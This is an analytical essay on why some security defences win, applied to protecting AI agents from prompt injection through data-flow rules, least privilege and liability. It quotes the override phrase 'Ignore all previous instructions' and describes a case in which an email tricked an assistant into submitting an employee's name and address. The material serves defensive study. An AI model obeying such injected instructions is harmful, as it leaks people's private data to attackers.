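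*Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026) reports that Anthropic responded by cutting off live web access for its internal evaluations. A company whose agent books travel or answers customers' questions cannot do the same without ending the service.

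## What the winning defences share

Cryptography, parameterised queries and memory-safe languages block very different attacks, but they share several features that malware detectors and spam filters lack. Agents can have most of these features too, though mainly in the code around the model. The comparison rests on a few cases, and there are good reasons to question how far it applies to agents.

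### Six features

Six features might explain why a defence wins:

- Exact property: the defender can state what must never happen precisely enough for a computer to check it.
- Mechanical check: a small piece of ordinary software or hardware enforces the property without judging anyone's intentions.
- Whole class: the defence blocks every attack of one kind, including attacks that nobody has invented yet.
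- Cost growth: a little more work for the defender makes far more work for the attacker.
- Cheap default: people get the protection without much effort or loss.
- Open testing: outsiders can attack the defence in public, and the defender can replace whatever breaks.

| Defence | Exact property | Mechanical check | Whole class | Cost growth | Cheap default | Open testing | Result so far |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
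| Encryption algorithms | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Won |
| Parameterised queries | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Partly | Yes | Won where used |
| Memory-safe languages | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | Yes, for new code | Yes | Won where used |
| seL4 | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | No | Yes | Strong but rarely used |
| Browser sandboxes | Yes | Partly | No | No | Yes | Yes | Need constant repairs |
| Malware detectors | No | No | No | No | Yes | Partly | Not won |
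| Spam filters | No | No | No | No | Yes | Partly | Tolerable |
| Robust image classifiers | Partly | No | No | No | No | Yes | Not won |
| Training and filtering against prompt injection | No | No | No | No | Partly | Partly | Not won |
| Fixed plans with labelled data | Partly | Yes | Partly | No | No | Partly | Too early to tell |
| Isolation and least privilege for agents | Yes | Partly | No | No | Partly | Partly | Depends on the job |

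A defence seems to need an exact property and a mechanical check to win. All three wins have both, while malware detectors, spam filters and trained defences against prompt injection have neither. The check depends on the property, because software can only enforce a rule mechanically if someone has stated it exactly.

The check doesn't always have to be small, because the amount of code an attacker can reach matters more than the total amount. The Rust compiler is a large program, but an attacker usually has no way to send it anything. A browser's privileged process and the Linux kernel, however, constantly have to handle hostile requests.

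Winning defences also tend to block a whole class of attacks. This is nearly true by definition, because one test for a win was that the defence lasts without a fresh fix for each new attack, but it is still useful advice. *Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?* (Williams-King, Le and colleagues, 2025) argues that defenders cannot win an arms race in which code and data have no clear boundary, and should move to an environment where the race doesn't arise. It predicted that attackers would keep beating language models until defenders did something similar. According to the paper, the phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" worked against OpenAI's leading models for 22 months.

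Only cryptography makes the attacker's work grow much faster than the defender's. Adi Shamir, one of the inventors of RSA, said in a 2003 lecture that in security generally, you have to double your expenditure to halve your vulnerability (Kabay, 2004, *RSA founders give perspective on cryptography*). Under that rule, making a system 1,000 times less vulnerable costs 1,000 times as much. By contrast, adding ten bits to a cipher's key makes a brute-force search about 1,000 times longer, with very little extra computation for the defender. Schneier draws the same contrast in *The Intersection of Encryption and AI* and describes the rest of computer security as a fast arms race with fragile defences.

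That describes patching well, but not parameterised queries. A programmer writes the query once, and an attacker gains nothing by working harder because the defence rules the attack out. Making attacks harder is therefore useful only where they remain possible in principle.

Making a defence easy to run and turning it on by default won't make it effective, as malware detectors show. But without those two properties, even an excellent defence may stay rare. seL4 has almost every other property in the table, yet few organisations use it.

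Open testing is not enough by itself, since researchers test image classifiers in public and keep breaking them. Open testing matters most in cryptography, where nobody can prove the underlying assumptions. *In the age of AI and quantum computing, we need more cryptography* (Goldwasser, 2026) says that confidence must rest on the ability of systems to withstand scrutiny and evolve, "not on the absence of attacks". *How to Respond Not if but When Encryption Algorithms Are Put to the Test* (Knodel, 2026) describes cryptography as a field designed around the possibility of its own obsolescence.

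A planned change to Chrome is an example of replacement. Browsers trust a website's key because a certificate authority has signed it. Google's *Keeping HTTPS Connections Safe in Chrome* (2026) announced on 3 December a plan for Chrome to stop trusting authorities' keys that use P-256, a common elliptic curve, from 15 March 2027. Affected websites will have to get a new certificate from an authority with a different kind of key, or their visitors will see a full-page warning. The websites need no other changes.

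### Which features agents can have

Developers don't know how to build an exact property or a mechanical check into a language model, which has to interpret English to do its job. So they can't show that training has removed a whole class of attacks.

Williams-King and colleagues add that developers usually train a model for safety after it has learned everything else. They compare this with BGP, which routes traffic between the networks that make up the internet. Its designers did not plan for dishonest networks, so a network can divert other people's traffic by announcing false routes. Redesigning BGP now would be very expensive.

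The code around the model can have both features, so it can rule out whole classes of harmful action, though not false summaries.

Nobody has found a setting in a model that multiplies the attacker's work while adding little to the developer's. The code around the model can get that advantage by using cryptography. If a bank accepts large payments only with an accountant's digital signature, a hijacked agent cannot forge the signature however many times it tries, though it may still trick the accountant into signing.

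Both the model and the software around it can protect users by default. A company that trains its model to resist injections protects every user, and the makers of agent software can ship it with a sandbox switched on. Outsiders can also test both, but the software is easier to repair. Programmers can replace one faulty check without changing the others, whereas training against injections made one model in He and colleagues' study abandon many ordinary tasks.

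### An exact rule for private data

"Do what the user wants" has no exact specification. Someone who tells an agent to deal with their email wants it to answer some messages and ignore others, and may not know which until they see the result.

"Send no private data to unapproved recipients" is more promising. Suppose that every piece of data carries a list of permitted readers, as in CaMeL. The rule is then

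recipients(m) ⊆ readers(m), for every message m that the agent sends

Ordinary code can check whether a message's destination is on an approved list without knowing why the agent wants to send it. This rule would stop an attack described in OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026). The attacker's email looked like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring, and asked the user's assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked half the time in testing. A filter would have to recognise that the email's story was false, whereas code enforcing the rule would block the submission because the destination is not on the list.

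ChatGPT has an approximate version of the rule, called Safe Url. It is designed to detect when the agent is about to send information from the conversation to a third party. It then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transfer and prompts the agent to try another way.

Someone still has to fill in the lists, which is difficult. Suppose a user asks an agent to book dinner for four and mention any allergies. The agent finds a private note that one guest cannot eat nuts. A message based on the note can go only to people allowed to read the note. The restaurant is not on that list, so the rule blocks a message that everyone would want the agent to send. If the user adds the restaurant, the rule also lets the agent send it the rest of the note. Whether sharing is appropriate depends on the purpose as well as the recipient, and the rule was supposed to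 avoid the need to judge purposes. The rule also does not stop an agent from revealing a secret by whether it sends a message at all.

These are real gaps, but the winning defences have similar ones. Parameterised queries enforce something much narrower than "run only the queries that the company wants", which nobody ever specified, and memory-safe programs can still contain any number of logic errors. In both cases the exact property left out much of what people wanted, but covered a common and serious kind of attack. Certified robustness for images shows how an exact property can be too narrow, because attackers can easily make changes larger than the certificate covers.

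The rule about recipients looks more like the parameterised query when the agent has a narrow job. An agent that handles invoices from 20 known suppliers rarely needs to write to anyone else. A general assistant often writes to new people, so its user would have to grant so many exceptions that the rule might protect very little.

### Cases chosen after the fact

It is easy to find a pattern among successes in hindsight. The three clear wins in the table and the malware, spam, image and trained prompt-injection defences make seven cases. A feature unrelated to success, and present in each case with a probability of one half, would match all seven results by luck once in 128 times. Someone who considered 100 such features would have a 54% chance of finding at least one that matched.

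Including unsuccessful cases partly guards against this, although hindsight influenced the choice of those cases too. A better test is to look for other cases that break the pattern.

DVD copy protection had an exact rule, that only licensed players could decrypt a disc, and enforced it with encryption. In 1999 programmers got a key from a software player and published a program that decrypted the discs. The cipher was weak, but the deeper problem was that every player contained a key, so the people the film studios wanted to restrict already had one. This case shows that the attacker must not control the machine that enforces the rule, a condition the six features leave out. An agent that runs on its operator's servers can meet that condition.

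Secure operating systems for the US military are a more worrying case. In the 1980s the Department of Defense published standards for systems that enforced exact rules about who could read classified data. The highest rating required a mathematically verified design. Digital Equipment Corporation built a small kernel for that rating but cancelled it in 1990, before its commercial release, partly because the company expected too few customers. The labels that CaMeL attaches to data descend from this work, and companies could abandon them too if they prove too inconvenient.

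Some defences also partly succeed without an exact property. Banks use statistical models to detect card fraud, and keep losses below 0.1% of spending. They have to update the models constantly, so this defence fails the test for a win. But customers can dispute a payment and banks can reverse it, which makes the remaining fraud tolerable. Agents whose actions are easy to undo could be safe enough for the same reason.

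### Attackers who go round the barrier

In the same lecture, Shamir said that "Cryptography is typically bypassed, not penetrated." He knew of no major security failure in which hackers had relied on heavy codebreaking, since they usually had much easier methods. A defence that defeats one kind of attack may therefore just lead attackers to try another.

An attacker with several ways in will tend to choose the cheapest:

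cost of attack = min(c₁, c₂, …, cₙ)

If stealing a company's data costs $1,000 by SQL injection and $5,000 by tricking an employee, eliminating SQL injection raises the attacker's cost only to $5,000. That win is limited but still useful, because some attackers won't find the data worth $5,000. The routes also differ in scale. A broken cipher could expose the recorded messages of millions of people, while a phisher has to fool each victim.

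Deception is profitable. In business email compromise, an attacker typically poses as an executive or a supplier and persuades staff to send money. The FBI's Internet Crime Complaint Center (IC3) puts losses from this crime at $3 billion in 2025.

However, recent figures do not show a simple move from software to people. Verizon, a telecoms company, publishes a yearly study of data breaches. Help Net Security's *Verizon DBIR* (2026) reports that software vulnerabilities have overtaken stolen credentials as the most common way for attackers to get in, for the first time in the study's 19 years. Vulnerabilities were the starting point for 31% of breaches, up from 20% a year earlier (Infosecurity Magazine, *Verizon DBIR*), and stolen credentials for 13% (Underhill, *2026 Verizon DBIR*, 2026). The 13% covers only breaches where stolen credentials were the first step. Passwork, which sells password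 software, notes that attackers abused credentials at some point in 39% of breaches.

Verizon's researchers blame slow patching more than AI for the change, according to CPO Magazine's *Verizon 2026 DBIR*. The average time to patch a flaw had grown by almost two weeks, and the incidents they studied ran only to October 2025, before Mythos Preview existed. Attackers evidently return to attacking software when its flaws stay unpatched long enough.

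An attacker who cannot make an agent send out private data might feed it false information, trick the person who approves its requests, or break into the system that stores its credentials. If one of these attacks is much easier than the others, strengthening the defences against the others achieves little.

### Slow wins and fast-moving agents

Past wins took decades. Researchers published the idea of public-key cryptography in 1976, yet in 2015 most pages people loaded in Chrome were still unencrypted. Agents are spreading much faster. OpenAI launched its Atlas browser in October 2025, and by December researchers had shown that a few words hidden in a Google Doc could manipulate its agent, according to Fortune (2025).

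*Talent Isn't a Security Strategy*, an essay by an engineer who worked on early versions of Internet Explorer, compares agents with the browsers of the 1990s. Microsoft was racing Netscape, and its ActiveX technology let web pages use components designed for use inside Windows. One component could install a root certificate, which tells the computer whom to trust when it checks a website's identity. The main protection was a prompt that asked the user to approve the component.

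Much of the delay in earlier cases came from slow adoption of defences that already existed. The essay credits the decline of SQL injection to safer defaults, libraries and automated scanning, rather than to training every developer to be perfect. The few companies that make most of the leading agents can change a default for millions of users with one update. Chrome is giving websites only about three months to replace certificates that depend on P-256.

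Defaults will do less to protect the connections organisations are now building themselves. A company that gives an agent broad access to its email and finance systems this year may find that access as hard to restrict later as old C code is to replace.

### What restrictions cost

Programmers lost almost nothing when they switched to parameterised queries, but defences for agents can greatly reduce what the agents get done. In Garby and colleagues' tests, CaMeL's policies cut the share of tasks completed with GPT-5.2 from 67% to 38%. This loss of usefulness is probably the most important difference between defending agents and the earlier wins.

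A restriction is worth having if the tasks it prevents are worth less than the attacks it prevents:

(c₀ − c₁) × v < (q₀ − q₁) × L

c is the share of tasks completed, v is the value of a task, q is the chance that an attack succeeds during a task, and L is the loss when it does. The subscripts 0 and 1 mean without and with the restriction. Suppose a task is worth $5 and a hijacking costs $10,000. A fall in completion from 67% to 38% then costs $1.45 per task, so the policies are worth using if they prevent at least one hijacking in about 7,000 tasks. In CaMeL's original tests, completion fell less, from 84% to 77%. That fall costs 35 cents per task, so preventing one hijacking in about 29,000 tasks is enough to justify it.

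Whether either loss is worth accepting therefore depends on the agent's job. The larger loss could easily be worth accepting for an agent that pays invoices from strangers' emails, but even the smaller one probably isn't for an agent that sorts photographs.

Some lost abilities may also return in a safer form. Browsers eventually abandoned ActiveX, but web pages can now do many things developers wanted from it. A video-call site, for example, can ask to use the camera without getting access to the rest of the computer.

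### Staff can be deceived too

Companies already depend on people whom outsiders can deceive. OpenAI compares an agent with a customer service worker who can issue refunds. Some customers will falsely claim that a refund never arrived, or make threats. The worker's employer expects some of them to succeed, so its software limits how much any customer can be refunded. OpenAI recommends placing the same controls on an agent as a person in its position would have.

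Many companies require two people to approve a large payment, which helps most when the two make different mistakes. Two copies of the same model acting as approvers would provide much less protection, because a text that fools one will probably fool the other. An accountant who phones the supplier on a number already on file would be a better second approver, because the accountant would be using different information.

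The Decoder calls OpenAI's comparison of prompt injection with scams misleading, because scams exploit human weaknesses such as inattention, trust and time pressure, whereas prompt injection exploits a technical flaw in the architecture of language models. This difference is a good reason not to expect agents to learn caution the way people do, but it is a weaker objection to outside controls, since a limit on the refunds an agent can issue caps the loss whatever caused the mistake.

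Scale is a bigger difference between employees and agents. Suppose 1,000 employees receive a message asking for a fraudulent refund, and the message would fool 3% of people. About 30 will issue the refund. If 1,000 copies of one agent receive the message, the number could be close to zero or close to 1,000, because the copies tend to respond alike. With a daily refund limit of $500 per agent, the company could lose $500,000 in a day, so it also needs a limit on the total. An attacker can also practise on an agent thousands of times, and the threat of dismissal or prison does not deter the agent.

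Employers also have some advantages with agents. They can record everything an agent does, cancel every copy's access at once, and grant new, very narrow permissions for each task, which few employees would put up with. But the $3 billion lost to business email compromise suggests that the usual controls on staff are not a high standard to match.

### How HTTPS became normal

People may not adopt a good defence if the work and expense fall on them and the benefit goes to someone else. HTTPS, which encrypts web connections, had this problem. Website owners generally had to buy a certificate, install it by hand and remember to renew it, while much of the benefit went to their visitors.

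In September 2015 a non-profit service called Let's Encrypt began issuing free certificates automatically. ISRG (2025), which runs it, reports that the worldwide share of Firefox page loads using HTTPS rose from below 30% to around 80% in about five years. *HTTPS by default* (Thompson, Acer and colleagues, 2025) reports that the share in Chrome rose from 30–45% in 2015 to 95–99% around 2020.

Let's Encrypt's executive director acknowledges that it cannot take all the credit (Aas, 2025, *A Note from our Executive Director*). Browser makers were pressing websites to encrypt at the same time. Chrome first showed a "not secure" warning only on unencrypted pages that collected passwords or credit card numbers, then extended it to any unencrypted page where someone entered data. Google's *Say “yes” to HTTPS* reports that over one year of this campaign, the protected share of Chrome traffic on Android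 rose from 42% to 64%, and the number of top 100 websites that used HTTPS by default rose from 37 to 71. Because the free certificates and the warnings overlapped, we can't tell from these figures how much each contributed.

Progress then stalled, partly because the warning was weak. *Chrome Now Warns Before Insecure HTTP Connections* (DeBlasio, Trouton and colleagues, 2026) points out that users can overlook it, and that it appears only after the connection has exposed their data. Many of the remaining sites used an unencrypted page only to redirect visitors to an encrypted one, and did so too quickly for any warning to appear. Thompson and colleagues found that many of the organisations responsible had never given the switch any attention, though it wasn't especially hard for them.

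In October 2026 Chrome began asking for permission before opening unencrypted public sites. In an earlier trial, the median user saw less than one warning a week, and 95% of users saw fewer than three. In 2015 the same rule would have interrupted people constantly, and they would probably have learned to click through the warnings.

Agent developers could follow the same order by first making isolation and narrow permissions free and automatic, then warning people about agents that lack them, and blocking those agents only once they are rare. If developers started with warnings, people would probably dismiss most of them, just as Claude Code's users approve 97% of its requests. Isolation and narrow permissions can limit what an agent does, however, whereas a website that switches to HTTPS generally still does everything it did before.

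Liability can also give the people who can improve security a reason to do so. Anderson's 2001 paper compares how banks responded to disputed withdrawals from cash machines. The burden of proof fell on the bank in the United States and on the customer in Britain. American banks spent less on security but suffered less fraud, because they had a reason to spend the money well.

It is often unclear who should pay when an agent causes a loss. If the agent was following malicious instructions in an email, the user, the employer, the model's developer and the maker of the email tool can all blame one another. The EU's revised Product Liability Directive gave member states until 9 December 2026 to make producers of defective software, including AI systems, liable for injury, damage to property and the destruction of personal data, but it does not cover purely financial losses. Someone whose agent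 paid a fraudster would need another legal basis for a claim, such as a contract.
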